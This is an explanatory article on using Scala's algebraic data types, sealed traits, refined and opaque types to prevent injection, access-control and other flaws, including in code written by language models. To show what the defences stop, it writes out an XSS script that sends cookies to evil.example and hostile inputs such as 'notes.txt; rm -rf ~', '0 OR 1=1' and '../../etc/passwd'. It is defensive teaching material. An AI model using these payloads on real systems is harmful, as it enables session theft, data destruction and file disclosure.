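# Using algebraic data types, refined types and sealed traits to rule out vulnerabilities in code written by language models

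## What do algebraic data types, sealed traits and refined types do?

Algebraic data types, sealed traits and refined types are ways of describing data that let the compiler reject code that would produce data the programmer did not mean to allow. An algebraic data type (ADT) builds a new type from simpler ones, either by grouping them together or by offering a choice between them. In Scala, a sealed trait declares such a choice and prevents later additions to it. A refined type narrows an existing type with a condition, as in "a whole number from 0 to 120". ML and Haskell programmers have used algebraic data types for decades, and Rust, Swift, Kotlin and recent versions of Java all have some form of them.

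These features matter for security because many vulnerabilities involve a value that should not exist at that point in the program, such as script inside a plain name or a negative quantity in an order. A programmer or language model can check for such values in every place they might appear, but will eventually miss one. Defining the data so that nobody can build a bad value turns a forgotten check into a compiler error.

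### What the compiler checks

Compile time is when the compiler reads the source code, before the program runs. Run time is when the program handles real input. In static type checking, which happens at compile time, the compiler checks that the code uses each value only as its type allows. Two calls to a small Scala function show what this check does and does not catch.

```scala
def birthYear(age: Int): Int = 2026 - age

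birthYear("thirty")  // does not compile: String where Int is required
birthYear(-5)        // compiles, and returns 2031
```

Without extra tools, Python would report the first mistake only when the program reached that line. Scala's compiler finds it in every branch of the code, including branches that no test ever runs, and needs no sample input. The check is somewhat crude, though. The compiler rejects `val n: Int = if true then 1 else "one"`, although the string could never end up in `n`. It also accepts `List.empty[Int].head`, which tries to take the first element of an empty list and crashes at run time.

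The type checker accepts the call with -5 because -5 is an `Int`. A type is roughly a set of permitted values, and `Int` permits about four billion whole numbers, most of which are not ages. The checker enforces whatever types the programmer chooses, so it can catch more errors when those types permit fewer values.

### A session with eight shapes

Suppose a web application keeps a record of who is making each request. A first attempt in Scala might look like this:

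```scala
case class Session(
  userId: Option[String],
  token: Option[String],
  isAdmin: Boolean
)
```

A `case class` is a record with named fields. An `Option[String]` field holds either a string or nothing, and a `Boolean` field holds true or false. Each of these fields has two shapes, so a record with three of them has 2 × 2 × 2 = 8 shapes.

| User id | Token | Admin flag | What it would mean |
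|---|---|---|---|
| absent | absent | false | a guest |
| absent | absent | true | an administrator who is nobody |
| absent | present | false | a login token with no owner |
| absent | present | true | the same, with administrator rights |
| present | absent | false | a named user who never logged in |
| present | absent | true | a named administrator who never logged in |
| present | present | false | a logged-in user |
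| present | present | true | a logged-in administrator |

The application needs three of these: the guest, the logged-in user and the logged-in administrator. The other five are invalid states, which the program's rules forbid but its types permit. Three of the five have the admin flag set, so a function that checks only that flag would treat all three as administrators.

The repair is to write down the three cases that the application needs and nothing else.

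```scala
sealed trait Session
case object Guest extends Session
final case class LoggedIn(userId: String, token: String) extends Session
final case class Admin(userId: String, token: String) extends Session
```

A trait is a type that other types can extend. Here three types extend `Session`, so a session is now a `Guest`, a `LoggedIn` or an `Admin`. A guest has no fields. A logged-in user must have both an id and a token, because the `LoggedIn` constructor requires both. Code can no longer build any of the five bad rows of the table, such as an administrator without a token, except by using `null`, the empty reference that Scala inherits from Java and allows unless the programmer switches on a stricter mode.

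This is an algebraic data type. Fields side by side ("an id and a token") form a product type, and alternatives ("a guest or a user") form a sum type. The names describe how to count a type's possible values. If there are U possible user ids and T possible tokens, the first record has (U + 1) × (T + 1) × 2 possible values, where each + 1 is the empty option. The sealed version has 1 + UT + UT, which is 2U + 2T + 1 fewer.

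The word `sealed` adds something that an ordinary trait lacks. Every direct subtype of a sealed trait has to stand in the same source file, so the compiler can list them all. (Scala 3 has a shorter notation, `enum`, with the same effect.) With that list in hand it can perform an exhaustiveness check, which compares the cases that a piece of code handles with the cases that exist. Here is a function with a gap:

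```scala
def canDeleteAccounts(s: Session): Boolean = s match
  case Guest       => false
  case Admin(_, _) => true
```

The compiler warns that the match may not be exhaustive and names `LoggedIn` as the missing case. Without the warning, the program would run normally until the first ordinary user reached this function, and then throw an exception. The check is most useful when the data type changes. If someone adds a fourth case, say `Suspended`, the compiler flags every match that does not handle it. *Illegal States* (2023), a lecture by Puppe, Herrmann and Gehrke for a functional programming course at the University of Würzburg, lists forcing compiler errors when the model changes as one of its techniques.

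In Scala, a failed check produces only a warning by default, so the code still runs unless a compiler option turns warnings into errors. A catch-all line such as `case _ => true` silences the check completely, because it covers every case, including any added later. The compiler also doesn't verify that each case returns the right answer. A version that returned `true` for `LoggedIn` would compile without warnings and let every logged-in user delete accounts.

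### Putting a condition on a value

`Admin("", "")` still compiles with the new `Session`, because the empty string is a string. Listing every acceptable id as a separate case would be impractical, so ruling out the empty string requires a way to restrict an existing type.

"Refined type" and "refinement type" usually mean the same thing. In standard notation, a refinement type has the form {x : T | C} and contains the values x of type T for which the condition C holds. For example, a type for ages could be {x : Int | 0 ≤ x and x ≤ 120}. *Refinement Types for Secure Implementations* (2010) uses this notation for a type system built on the language F#.

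In Scala, though, the phrase has two senses. The older one is structural. A Scala programmer can take a type and add required members to it, as in `AnyRef { def close(): Unit }`, which covers any object that has a `close` method, and the language has long called this addition a refinement. It constrains which operations an object offers and cannot express "from 0 to 120". The other sense is the one in the notation above, a base type plus a condition, and Scala programmers get it from libraries, chiefly "refined" and the newer "iron", which is for Scala 3. A request for "refined types" in Scala is therefore slightly ambiguous, although in discussions of security it nearly always means the conditions. With iron, an age looks like this:

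```scala
import io.github.iltotore.iron.*
import io.github.iltotore.iron.constraint.all.*

type AgeRange = GreaterEqual[0] & LessEqual[120]
type Age = Int :| AgeRange

val a: Age = 34   // compiles
val b: Age = -5   // does not compile

def readAge(n: Int): Either[String, Age] =
  n.refineEither[AgeRange]
```

The compiler can check the lines for `a` and `b` because the numbers are written in the source code. It cannot check `n`, which might come from a web form, so the library tests such values at run time and returns an `Either` containing an error message or a valid `Age`. The code that called `readAge` has to handle both outcomes before it can use the number. Some research languages can prove conditions about computed values at compile time, but these two libraries do not.

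A programmer can get much the same protection without a library by writing a smart constructor, a function that checks its input before creating a value of a type and is meant to be the only way to create one. This works only if the rest of the program can't create such values without calling the function, and Scala 3's opaque types enforce that restriction.

```scala
object Ages:
  opaque type Age = Int

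  object Age:
    def from(n: Int): Either[String, Age] =
      if n >= 0 && n <= 120 then Right(n)
      else Left(s"$n is not between 0 and 120")

  extension (a: Age) def toInt: Int = a
```

Inside the object `Ages`, an `Age` is an `Int`, so `from` can return `n` directly. Outside, the compiler treats `Age` and `Int` as unrelated types, so `val x: Ages.Age = 200` does not compile and other code has to call `from`. At run time the value is still a plain integer, so the check on types takes no extra memory. With an ordinary alias, `type Age = Int` without the word `opaque`, other code could use any `Int` as an `Age`. Scala 2 has no opaque types, so programmers usually wrap the value in a class with a private constructor.

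The compiler does not check whether the condition in this code is correct. If the programmer had typed `n <= 1200`, the program would still compile, and every function that takes an `Age` would rely on a bad check. But the pattern puts the check in one place, so a reviewer who wants to know whether an invalid age can reach the billing code needs to read only one short function instead of the whole program.

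The choice between the two approaches depends partly on how complicated the rules are. *Making Illegal States Unrepresentable* (Hillel Wayne, 2020) compares them using an address book in which every contact must have an email address or a postal address. The programmer can define three cases (email only, post only, both) so that only valid contacts can exist, which Wayne calls constructive. Alternatively, the programmer can keep two optional fields and add a test that at least one is present, which he calls predicative. The constructive version is safer because there are no invalid values to filter out, but it becomes harder to maintain as rules accumulate. Wayne illustrates this by adding three kinds of phone number, a rule that people without email need both a postal address and a phone, and a secret question that is only sometimes compulsory. Adding a test is much easier than reworking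 a set of cases, but the tests work on a larger set of possible values, most of them invalid, so an invalid value can get through more easily.

Sometimes a better data structure avoids the choice. In Wayne's example, a person has a set of friends and a set of enemies, and nobody may be in both. With two sets, code has to keep checking for overlap. A single table that maps each acquaintance to "friend" or "enemy" rules out overlap because it holds only one entry for each acquaintance.

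### Where the ideas come from

Refinement types began as a way to make the exhaustiveness check more precise. Tim Freeman and Frank Pfenning introduced them in 1991 for ML, a functional language whose compilers already warned about missing cases. These warnings were often false alarms. Freeman's doctoral thesis, *Refinement Types for ML* (1994), opens with a function that returns the last cell of a list and has no case for the empty list. An ML compiler warns about the missing case even if the program never passes the function an empty list. Freeman's system lets the programmer declare named subsets of a datatype, such as empty lists, lists of one element and longer lists. The checker then works out which subset each expression falls into, and warns only where the missing case might occur.

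Freeman's refinements are subsets of an algebraic data type, not integers with conditions, and the programmer has to declare each one. This restriction is deliberate, because a finite number of declared subsets guarantees that checking always finishes. The prototype took 22 seconds on a workstation of the day to check some routines for rewriting logical formulas, and it found an error in them.

Refinement types that attach a condition to a base type came later. Clancy's *Refinement Types, Annotated Bibliography* traces the development from Freeman and Pfenning to Hongwei Xi's Dependent ML, where the conditions are constraints from a small mathematical language, and then to Liquid Haskell (2014), where they are ordinary true-or-false program expressions. Scala's "refined" and "iron" libraries borrow that notation but omit most of the proving.

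The slogan "make illegal states unrepresentable" comes from Yaron Minsky, a programmer at Jane Street, a trading firm that writes much of its software in the ML dialect OCaml. Minsky's lecture "Effective ML" made the phrase popular, according to a Python tutorial named after the slogan. Wayne's address book example comes from F# for fun and profit's *Designing with types*, which credits Minsky for the phrase.

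Smart constructors are older than Alexis King's essay *Parse, don't validate* (2019), but the essay explains clearly why they help. King compares two Haskell functions that both reject an empty list. One returns nothing, and the program carries on with the same list as before, so only the programmer knows that it is non-empty. The other returns a value of a different type, `NonEmpty`, which consists of a first element plus a possibly empty remainder. King calls the first function a validator and the second a parser. If somebody later deletes the parser, the build fails because nothing produces the `NonEmpty` value that later functions require, whereas the program still compiles without the validator.

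King recommends data structures that exclude bad values by construction wherever feasible, and smart constructors as a fallback for cases like a number within a range. The essay also warns against the security risk of "shotgun parsing", a term from a 2016 paper on input-handling flaws. The term describes programs that scatter their input checks among the code that acts on the input. Such a program may act on part of a message before finding that another part is invalid.

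### How often models write vulnerable code

These design habits now appear in advice about model-written code. Khachaturov (2026), in the University of Cambridge lecture *Reliable Software and Security Engineering with Unreliable Tools*, recommends type checkers as an automatic first reviewer for such code, arguing that they take little effort to use once learned and do not depend on the code author's reasoning. Khachaturov also tells students that models are especially prone to shotgun parsing, but gives no measurements.

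*Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues, October 2026) measures how often language models write unsafe code. The researchers tested 32 models from seven families on 119 small programming tasks in C, C++, Go, JavaScript and Python. The tasks cover 31 entries of the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), the standard catalogue of software weaknesses. Each model attempted each task 100 times, which produced 380,800 programs, and the prompts did not mention security. The researchers ran every program against ordinary tests, to see whether it worked, and against an input built to trigger the weakness in question.

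Among the newest flagship models, the share of programs that worked but failed the attack test ranged from 13% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol to 28% for Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro. Since 94% of Gemini's programs worked, about three in ten of its working programs were insecure. Newer models did better than their predecessors, but some working programs from every model family were still insecure. On log injection, where an attacker forges a log entry by putting a line break in a message, nearly every model failed nearly every time. The Python programs that the researchers inspected wrote the incoming message into the log unchanged. A type checker assigns the same type to strings with and without line breaks.

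The study did not test Claude models or Scala, and its newest model dates from August 2026. Its design also limits what it can show about types, because each model was given the function's signature and wrote only the body, so it did not choose the types of its inputs. The range of 13% to 28% therefore applies to code written by models that had little room to redesign the data.

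## How does a type stop a vulnerability?

A type can stop a vulnerability when the dangerous operation accepts only values of that type, and the only way to make such a value is to perform the security check. For the log injection described above, cleaned messages would need their own type.

### A greeting that runs a script

Suppose a web page greets visitors by name and takes the name from the link they followed, such as `shop.example/hello?name=Ada`. The simplest code for this page joins strings.

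```scala
def greetingPage(name: String): String =
  "<p>Hello, " + name + "!</p>"
```

For Ada this returns `<p>Hello, Ada!</p>`. An attacker can send someone a link in which the name is a script:

```html
<script>fetch("https://evil.example/?c=" + document.cookie)</script>
```

The function puts this text into the page, and the victim's browser runs it as if the site's developers had written it. The script sends the attacker every cookie it can read, which may include the one that keeps the victim logged in. This is cross-site scripting (XSS), a form of injection, in which input meant as data runs as code.

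The usual defence is escaping, which replaces characters that have a special meaning in HTML with codes that the browser displays as text, so `<` becomes `&lt;`. Calling an escaping function inside `greetingPage` would fix this page, but a large site builds HTML in thousands of places, and the compiler accepts code that omits the call. Kern's *Securing the Tangled Web* (2014) describes script injection as "deceptively simple in cause and remedy" but very hard to prevent in large projects.

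The typed version gives escaped text its own opaque type.

```scala
object Html:
  opaque type SafeHtml = String

  def escape(s: String): SafeHtml =
    s.replace("&", "&amp;")
      .replace("<", "&lt;")
      .replace(">", "&gt;")
      .replace("\"", "&quot;")
      .replace("'", "&#39;")

  def greetingPage(name: SafeHtml): SafeHtml =
    "<p>Hello, " + name + "!</p>"

  def send(page: SafeHtml, out: java.io.Writer): Unit =
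    out.write(page)
```

Other code in the program receives the name as an ordinary `String`, and the program won't compile unless that code converts the name to the required type.

```scala
import Html.*

def handle(name: String, out: java.io.Writer): Unit =
  send(greetingPage(name), out)          // does not compile
  send(greetingPage(escape(name)), out)  // compiles
```

With the attacker's link, the second call sends a page that contains `&lt;script&gt;`. The visitor sees the script as text in the greeting, and nothing runs. The types also prevent double escaping. Because `escape` takes a `String`, `escape(escape(name))` does not compile, so nobody can escape a name twice and show visitors a stray `&amp;`. Public libraries use the same design. GWT's *Security Safe HTML*, part of the documentation for a toolkit for building web applications in Java, recommends a type that is also called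 `SafeHtml`.

### What the protection depends on

The protection depends on three conditions: only the smart constructor creates the value, every sink accepts only that type, and no code uses an escape hatch. A sink is an operation where bad data does harm, here writing the page. An escape hatch is a language feature that switches off type checks. If any condition fails, the script can get into the page again, and the program still compiles.

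Outside `Html`, the only way to turn a name into `SafeHtml` is to call the smart constructor, `escape`. If `SafeHtml` were declared as `final case class SafeHtml(value: String)`, any code could write `SafeHtml(name)`, which labels the raw script as safe without escaping it. Making the case class's constructor `private` doesn't prevent this under Scala 2's default settings, because the compiler also generates a public `apply` method that calls the constructor.

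**Every sink demands the type.** The underlying `out.write` still takes any string, so this line compiles anywhere that has access to the writer:

```scala
out.write("<p>Hello, " + name + "!</p>")
```

A team can hide the writer from application code, or add a build rule that rejects direct calls to it. Both approaches require someone to find all the sinks. Kotowicz (2021) writes in *Trusted Types*, a report on Google's work, that a page's own scripts can cause XSS through around 60 browser functions.

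The template compiler in Angular, a widely used web framework, decides what checks a value needs based on where it will appear, but its rules have had gaps. According to OSV's *GHSA-jrmj-c5cx-3cw6* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, the rules did not recognise that the link attributes of script elements inside SVG images load code. If an application put user input there, an attacker could run a script of their choice. Angular's developers fixed this in January 2026. In June, NVD's *CVE-2026-50557* (2026) recorded a similar gap for script elements written with a prefix, as in `<svg:script>`.

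**No code uses an escape hatch.** In Scala, `greetingPage(name.asInstanceOf[SafeHtml])` compiles. At run time a `SafeHtml` is a string, so the cast succeeds and any script in `name` goes into the page unescaped. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) gives a TypeScript example. A two-step cast makes the compiler treat the browser's `document.location` as an ordinary object with a text field, so its security check accepts an assignment that runs a script.

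### What the compiler guarantees

The compiler checks only that every argument to `greetingPage` and `send` has the type `SafeHtml`. It never processes the attacker's name. The server makes the five replacements later, each time somebody opens the page. If the program compiles and the three conditions hold, no name reaches `send` without going through `escape`. But the compiler would not catch a mistake in `escape`, just as it would not catch the mistyped age limit. If the line that replaces `<` were missing, the program would still compile and the script would run.

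Kern (2025), in *Safe Coding*, explains the design through preconditions, a standard idea in program verification. Let P(x) mean that a browser can display x without running any code that an outsider chose. Writing x to the page is safe only if P(x) holds. With plain strings, a reviewer has to establish P(x) at every write, which can mean tracing x back through the whole program. The typed version turns P into a property of every value of the type:

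for all w of type `SafeHtml`, P(w)

This follows by a short induction. `escape(s)` satisfies P for any string s, because its result contains no character that could open a tag. `greetingPage(n)` satisfies P whenever n does, because it only places n between two fixed pieces of HTML. No other function creates a `SafeHtml`. A person has to check these steps, but they cover fewer than twenty lines of code.

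A run-time check inside `send` could not replace this. A program can check some unsafe operations on the spot. For example, it can tell whether a position in a list is valid from the position and the list's length. But Kern points out that the safety of a query or a page depends on where its parts came from, which a string does not record. In a finished page, a script tag the developer wrote looks the same as one the attacker supplied. The check has to happen while the two are still separate, and the type carries the result to the sink.

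### Why HTML, SQL and shell commands need different types

Escaping text for HTML makes it safe in one position on a web page, but the same text can be harmful elsewhere. The inputs below contain none of the five characters that `escape` replaces, so they pass through unchanged.

| Input | Where it does harm | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| `javascript:alert(1)` | the address of a link | the script runs when someone clicks |
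| `0 OR 1=1` | after `WHERE user_id =` in a database query | the query matches every row |
| `notes.txt; rm -rf ~` | after `cat` in a shell command | the shell deletes the user's files |

Giving each of these uses its own type makes it a compile error to put a name escaped for a web page directly into a database query. If a single `SafeString` type covered them all, the compiler would allow it.

Browsers alone need several types, and Wang and colleagues use six: one each for HTML, scripts, addresses that a user may follow, addresses from which a page may load code, single style declarations and whole style sheets. Sometimes the right type depends on another value. A `<link>` element can point to an icon, which needs only an address that is safe to follow, or to a style sheet, which needs a trusted source. Google's library therefore sets the kind of link and its address in one call, so that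 the address must have the type that kind of link requires.

For SQL, the better type makes developers supply user input separately from the query instead of escaping it. Database libraries support this with placeholders, as in `SELECT y FROM table WHERE x = ?`, and the database never interprets the supplied value as SQL. Kern describes a Google type called `TrustedSqlString`, which developers can build only from text that appears in the program's own source code. Adding a user's input to the query therefore does not compile, so the developer has to use a placeholder. The equivalent for shell commands is to pass the program's name and a list of arguments directly to the operating system, without a shell to interpret them.

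A programmer can bypass even this type without a cast, by writing out a table of single characters, looking up each character of an untrusted string in it, and assembling a `TrustedSqlString` from the results. Kern reports that this is not a significant problem at Google, because the code looks so obviously wrong that trusted developers hardly ever write it. The method is meant to prevent accidents by well-meaning developers, and Kern rules out relying on it against an author trying to defeat it. A language model fits the assumption of a well-meaning author only if it does not use a cast or a workaround to clear a compiler error.

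### A value that proves a check took place

A type can also record an event. Many applications have an address like `/balance/8` that returns the balance of account 8, and a common flaw is to return it to whoever asks. Security engineers call this an insecure direct object reference. The input is a valid number, so escaping or range checks would not help. The code never checks whether the user may see the account.

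In the following code, the function that reads a balance requires evidence that the program has checked ownership. The code uses the three-case `Session` type from the previous section, and `owns` and `loadBalance` stand for private functions that query the database.

```scala
object Accounts:
  final class CanRead private[Accounts] (val accountId: Int)

  def authorize(s: Session, accountId: Int): Option[CanRead] =
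    val allowed = s match
      case Guest               => false
      case LoggedIn(userId, _) => owns(userId, accountId)
      case Admin(_, _)         => true
    if allowed then Some(new CanRead(accountId)) else None

  def balance(permit: CanRead): BigDecimal =
    loadBalance(permit.accountId)
```

The call `balance(8)` does not compile because `balance` takes a `CanRead`, not an account number. Code outside `Accounts` can get a `CanRead` only by calling `authorize`, which returns an `Option`, so the code must also handle a refusal. `balance` uses the account number stored in the `CanRead`, so a programmer cannot check account 7 and then read account 8.

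*Type Level Security* (2026), an article by the security company Snyk, proposes the same pattern in Python and Rust as a defence for both human-written and AI-written code. In its example, the program cannot use the requested user id until it presents an `AuthenticationGuard`. But the function that issues the guard does not receive the requested id, and the guard does not record whose data it covers. As written, the types ensure that a login check took place, but they would still let a logged-in user request someone else's balance.

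The protection depends on the same three conditions as `SafeHtml`. Another function that queries the accounts table directly would bypass the permit. Privacy rules also vary in strength by language. Snyk notes that Python code can reach the hidden value without a guard, while Rust's rules prevent this. A `CanRead` value proves only that the check succeeded when it ran. If the program stores the permit for a day and the user loses access in the meantime, `balance` will still accept it.

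### What happened when Google built software this way

Google turned these ideas into company-wide rules for its JavaScript. Wang and colleagues describe the rollout, which began in early 2018 and targeted DOM-based XSS. In this kind of XSS, a script already on the page inserts the attacker's text in the browser, often by assigning it to `innerHTML`, the property that holds an element's HTML. Google extended its compilers to reject direct use of sinks like `innerHTML` and gave developers replacement functions that accept only the six safe types.

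Developers can make a safe value from text in the source code, with a sanitizer that strips out dangerous parts, or with a template system that escapes each value for its position. Another builder converts any string without checking it. At Google, the compiler treats this builder as a banned sink, so a security expert has to approve each use.

One product's team spent about a year converting its code. External researchers and others found 10 DOM-based XSS vulnerabilities in the product in the year before, 2 during the conversion and 1 in the year after. These numbers are small, and there was no comparison group. Across the company, DOM-based XSS made up a falling share of the serious vulnerabilities that outsiders reported, and a growing share of the remaining cases came from old code that did not use the new functions. This is consistent with the new code being safer, although Wang and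 colleagues acknowledge that other security measures may have contributed.

The approach took little expert time. In the first five months of wide adoption, the security team received fewer than eight exception requests a week, in a codebase with roughly 10,000 weekly changes involving JavaScript. To avoid breaking existing software, the team exempted old files automatically, and by the end of 2020 the exemptions covered less than 1% of more than a million files.

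Casts can defeat a compile-time check, so Google also proposed Trusted Types, a check that the browser performs at run time. It is now a web standard. MDN's *Trusted Types API* explains that a site turns it on by sending a particular header with its pages. The browser then refuses plain strings at the sinks.

```js
element.innerHTML = userInput;                     // throws a TypeError
element.innerHTML = policy.createHTML(userInput);  // allowed
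```

A cast makes no difference here, because it changes only how the compiler treats the string and does not turn it into a `TrustedHTML` object. However, the developer writes the `policy`, and the browser does not check whether it makes the string safe. The browser would accept even a policy that returned its input unchanged and so gave no protection.

Kotowicz reports that by mid-2021 Google had moved more than 130 services to Trusted Types and had seen no DOM-based XSS in them. Kotowicz also reviewed confirmed DOM-based XSS reports that outside researchers had sent to Google, and estimated that Trusted Types would have prevented at least 61% of them. The others came from bugs in sanitizers, an old framework that mixes templates with data, and old code that the migration had deliberately exempted. A sanitizer bug is like a faulty `escape` in that the check is wrong even though the type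 system works correctly.

The latest figures come from Kern, who reports that hundreds of Google web applications built on these frameworks have together averaged less than one XSS report a year over the past several years. Hundreds of applications that use the `TrustedSqlString` interfaces have had no reported SQL injection for more than a decade. Some vulnerabilities may go unreported because nobody has found them, but Google pays outsiders to look for them and has increased the rewards.

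It is harder to say how much of this is due to types. Google's *Secure by Design* lists some twenty protections that the frameworks switch on by default, including templates that escape data and limits on which scripts a browser will run. An attacker would have to get past several at once. The SQL result depends more directly on a single type, but Kern gives no count from before the change.

Few other sites have adopted Trusted Types, which has worked in the current versions of all major browsers only since February 2026. Helme (2026), in *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026*, checked the homepages of popular sites and found 170,057 that sent a content security policy, the header that carries the Trusted Types setting. Only 318 of them, about 0.2%, required Trusted Types. The count leaves out sites that use it only on inner pages, such as those behind a login.

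Part of the difficulty is writing the check itself. In *Trust Me If You Can* (2024), Roth, Gröber and colleagues asked 13 web developers to add Trusted Types to a small application. Switching it on only required copying and pasting one fixed header. The hard part was writing sanitizers that blocked attacks without breaking the site's advertisements, maps and other outside code. Off-the-shelf sanitizers remove all scripts, so many sites need custom ones, which are often faulty. Earlier research cited in the paper found 88 sanitizers that attackers could bypass, in use on 102 domains.

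## Which vulnerabilities can types rule out, and which can they not?

Types can rule out a vulnerability that occurs only when a bad value reaches a particular operation, or when the program skips a check that could have been recorded in a value. They help much less when every value is acceptable and the fault lies in the program's rules, its running time or something outside the program.

Much of what attackers exploit depends on bad values or skipped checks. The latest yearly ranking of software weaknesses from MITRE, the US non-profit that maintains the CWE catalogue, is *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025). It includes five kinds of injection, six kinds of memory error and five failures of access control. Injection and memory errors account for 79 of the 123 vulnerabilities in the ranking's counts that attackers are known to have exploited. Zorz (2026), in *CISA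 review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes*, reports that CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, wants software makers to eliminate such recurring weaknesses at the source instead of leaving defenders to cope with them.

### Numbers out of range and missing values

A shop that accepts an order for -3 chairs may end up paying the customer. A refined type for quantities prevents this, because the program rejects -3 before it creates an order. But the guarantee covers only that value, and arithmetic on it can produce a result outside the safe range.

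```scala
type AtLeastOne = Int :| GreaterEqual[1]

val quantity: AtLeastOne = 429497
val priceInCents: AtLeastOne = 10000

val total: Int = quantity * priceInCents   // 2704
```

The customer should pay 4,294,970,000 cents, or about 43 million dollars. Scala's `Int` stops at 2,147,483,647 and then wraps round to negative numbers. This total is large enough to wrap past them and back up to 2,704 cents, so the customer is charged $27.04 even though both inputs satisfy their type. Upper limits on the inputs would fix this. With at most 1,000 items at no more than 1,000,000 cents each, the total cannot exceed a billion cents, which fits in an `Int`. The programmer has to work out that the total fits, because the library does not check the multiplication.

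For missing values, `Option` addresses the null pointer error (CWE-476), which rose from 21st to 13th place in the ranking. Scala code can still fail, because `.get` crashes if the `Option` is empty and Java libraries can return `null` where the code expects a string.

### Injection and file paths

The typed interfaces for HTML and SQL from the previous section address the top two entries in the ranking. Shell command injection (CWE-78) stands ninth, but its 20 exploited vulnerabilities are the most of any entry. Passing a program's name and a list of arguments keeps the shell out of it, but the program that receives the arguments may still interpret them. Suppose a server searches a folder that the user names:

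```scala
Seq("find", folder, "-name", "*.log")
```

If the user enters `-delete` as the folder, the version of `find` on most Linux systems treats it as an instruction and deletes everything in the current directory. A refined type for folder names that rejects a leading hyphen would prevent this.

Algebraic data types help most directly with code injection (CWE-94), in which a program runs a user's text as code. For example, a calculator page might evaluate formulas by passing them to Python. Replacing this with a parser that produces a sealed set of cases, such as a number, a sum or a product, removes the vulnerability, because no case exists for reading a file or opening a network connection.

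Path traversal (CWE-22) is similar to injection, but the dangerous text is a file name. If a site serves files from `/srv/uploads`, a visitor can request `../../etc/passwd`, where each `..` means "go up one folder". A smart constructor can check which file the name leads to.

```scala
import java.nio.file.Path

object Uploads:
  opaque type UploadPath = Path
  private val root = Path.of("/srv/uploads")

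  def locate(name: String): Option[UploadPath] =
    val p = root.resolve(name).normalize()
    if p.startsWith(root) then Some(p) else None
```

`normalize()` removes the `..` steps, so the visitor's request becomes `/etc/passwd` and `locate` returns nothing. This check covers only the text of the path, so a path that starts with `/srv/uploads` can still lead elsewhere if the uploads folder contains a symbolic link, which is a small file that redirects to another location.

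### Permission and order

Missing authorization (CWE-862) rose from ninth place to fourth. The `CanRead` permit from the previous section addresses it. The insecure direct object reference in that example is listed separately as CWE-639, in 24th place.

Coding agents seem to need more help with authorization than with SQL. The security company Tenzai asked five agents, including Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, to build the same three applications. SecurityWeek reports that the 15 results contained 69 vulnerabilities, but no exploitable SQL injection or XSS. The agents handled basic authorization well and did worse as the rules became more complex. According to the study's summary for AppSec Day Israel (2026), the agents consistently used parameterized queries. Their code often displayed input without cleaning it, but the web frameworks prevented XSS anyway. Frameworks cannot do the same for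 authorization, because every application has its own rules. A permit type could force each lookup to go through a check, though Tenzai did not test this, and someone would still have to write the rules correctly.

Types can also enforce the order of operations. The method is to give each stage its own type, which programmers call typestate.

```scala
def pay(cart: Cart): Option[PaidOrder]
def ship(order: PaidOrder): Unit
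```

If `ship` requires a `PaidOrder` and only `pay` can create one, then `ship(cart)` does not compile. The same approach works for missing authentication (CWE-306), where a program performs a sensitive action before anyone has logged in. The function that performs the action can require a `LoggedIn` value instead of accepting any `Session`.

However, nothing in Scala prevents a program from calling `ship(order)` twice, because `order` is still available after the first call. In Rust, a function can take ownership of its argument, and the compiler then rejects any later use of that value by the caller. Rust's locks use related rules. A lock should let only one thread at a time use some data, and *Guards*, a Rust tutorial, explains how to make the data accessible only through a value that a thread gets by taking the lock, so a programmer can't forget to lock first.

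### Memory errors

In a memory error, a program reads or writes memory it should not use. In a use after free (CWE-416), for example, the program frees a block of memory and then keeps using it. An attacker who gets other data into that block in the meantime may be able to take control of the program. These errors mostly affect C and C++. Programs in Scala, Java or Python rarely have them, even when their data is badly designed, because those languages check list positions at run time and free memory only when nothing refers to it.

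Rust prevents use after free at compile time with ownership types, not algebraic data types. Every value has one owner, and the program frees the value's memory when the owner goes out of scope.

```rust
let a = vec![1, 2, 3];
let b = a;            // b now owns the list
println!("{:?}", a);  // does not compile
```

Rust's compiler rejects a reference that would outlive the value it points to. Algebraic data types do not help here, because a closed set of alternatives does not specify when memory is freed. Rust catches out-of-bounds indexes mainly with run-time checks, which stop the program before it touches neighbouring memory.

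Android's memory vulnerabilities fell from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024 (The Hacker News, 2025). Google's *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that in 2025 they made up less than 20% of Android's vulnerabilities for the first time. Google has found one potential memory vulnerability in Android's roughly 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million lines, compared with about 1,000 per million in Android's C and C++ code.

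The Rust figure is based on one known flaw, a buffer overflow in an image library called CrabbyAVIF, which Google fixed before release. The code is fairly new, so people have had less time to find other flaws, but 50 more would raise the figure only to about 10 per million lines, a hundredth of the C and C++ figure. About 4% of Android's Rust code is inside `unsafe` blocks, the main way for Rust programmers to perform operations that the compiler cannot check. Vander Stoep argues that even this code has fewer flaws than the same amount of C or C++.

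### The main classes side by side

The ranks and the counts of exploited vulnerabilities below come from MITRE.

| Weakness | Rank | Exploited | Type that helps | What it guarantees | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cross-site scripting (CWE-79) | 1 | 7 | Escaped HTML | No raw text reaches a typed sink | Faulty escaping, casts, sinks that take plain strings |
| SQL injection (CWE-89) | 2 | 4 | Query text from source code only | User input stays separate from the query | Queries that return too much |
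| Shell injection (CWE-78) | 9 | 20 | Program name and argument list | No shell interprets the input | Input that the program reads as an option |
| Path traversal (CWE-22) | 6 | 10 | Path checked against a folder | The path's text stays inside the folder | Symbolic links, changes after the check |
| Missing authorization (CWE-862) | 4 | 0 | Permit value | A check ran for this record | Wrong rules, outdated permits |
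| Missing authentication (CWE-306) | 21 | 11 | Logged-in session | Somebody logged in first | Entry points that do not require the type |
| Wrong order (CWE-696) | not ranked | – | One type per stage | Earlier steps have happened | Repeated steps, unless values are single-use |
| Null pointer (CWE-476) | 13 | 0 | `Option` | Code handles the missing case | Forced extraction, `null` from older libraries |
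| Bad input (CWE-20) | 18 | 2 | Refined type | The value is in range | Wrong limits, later arithmetic |
| Use after free (CWE-416) | 7 | 14 | Ownership | No use of freed memory | `unsafe` code |
| Out-of-bounds write (CWE-787) | 5 | 12 | Arrays with run-time checks | The program stops before a bad write | `unsafe` code, crashes |

### Correct types, wrong rules

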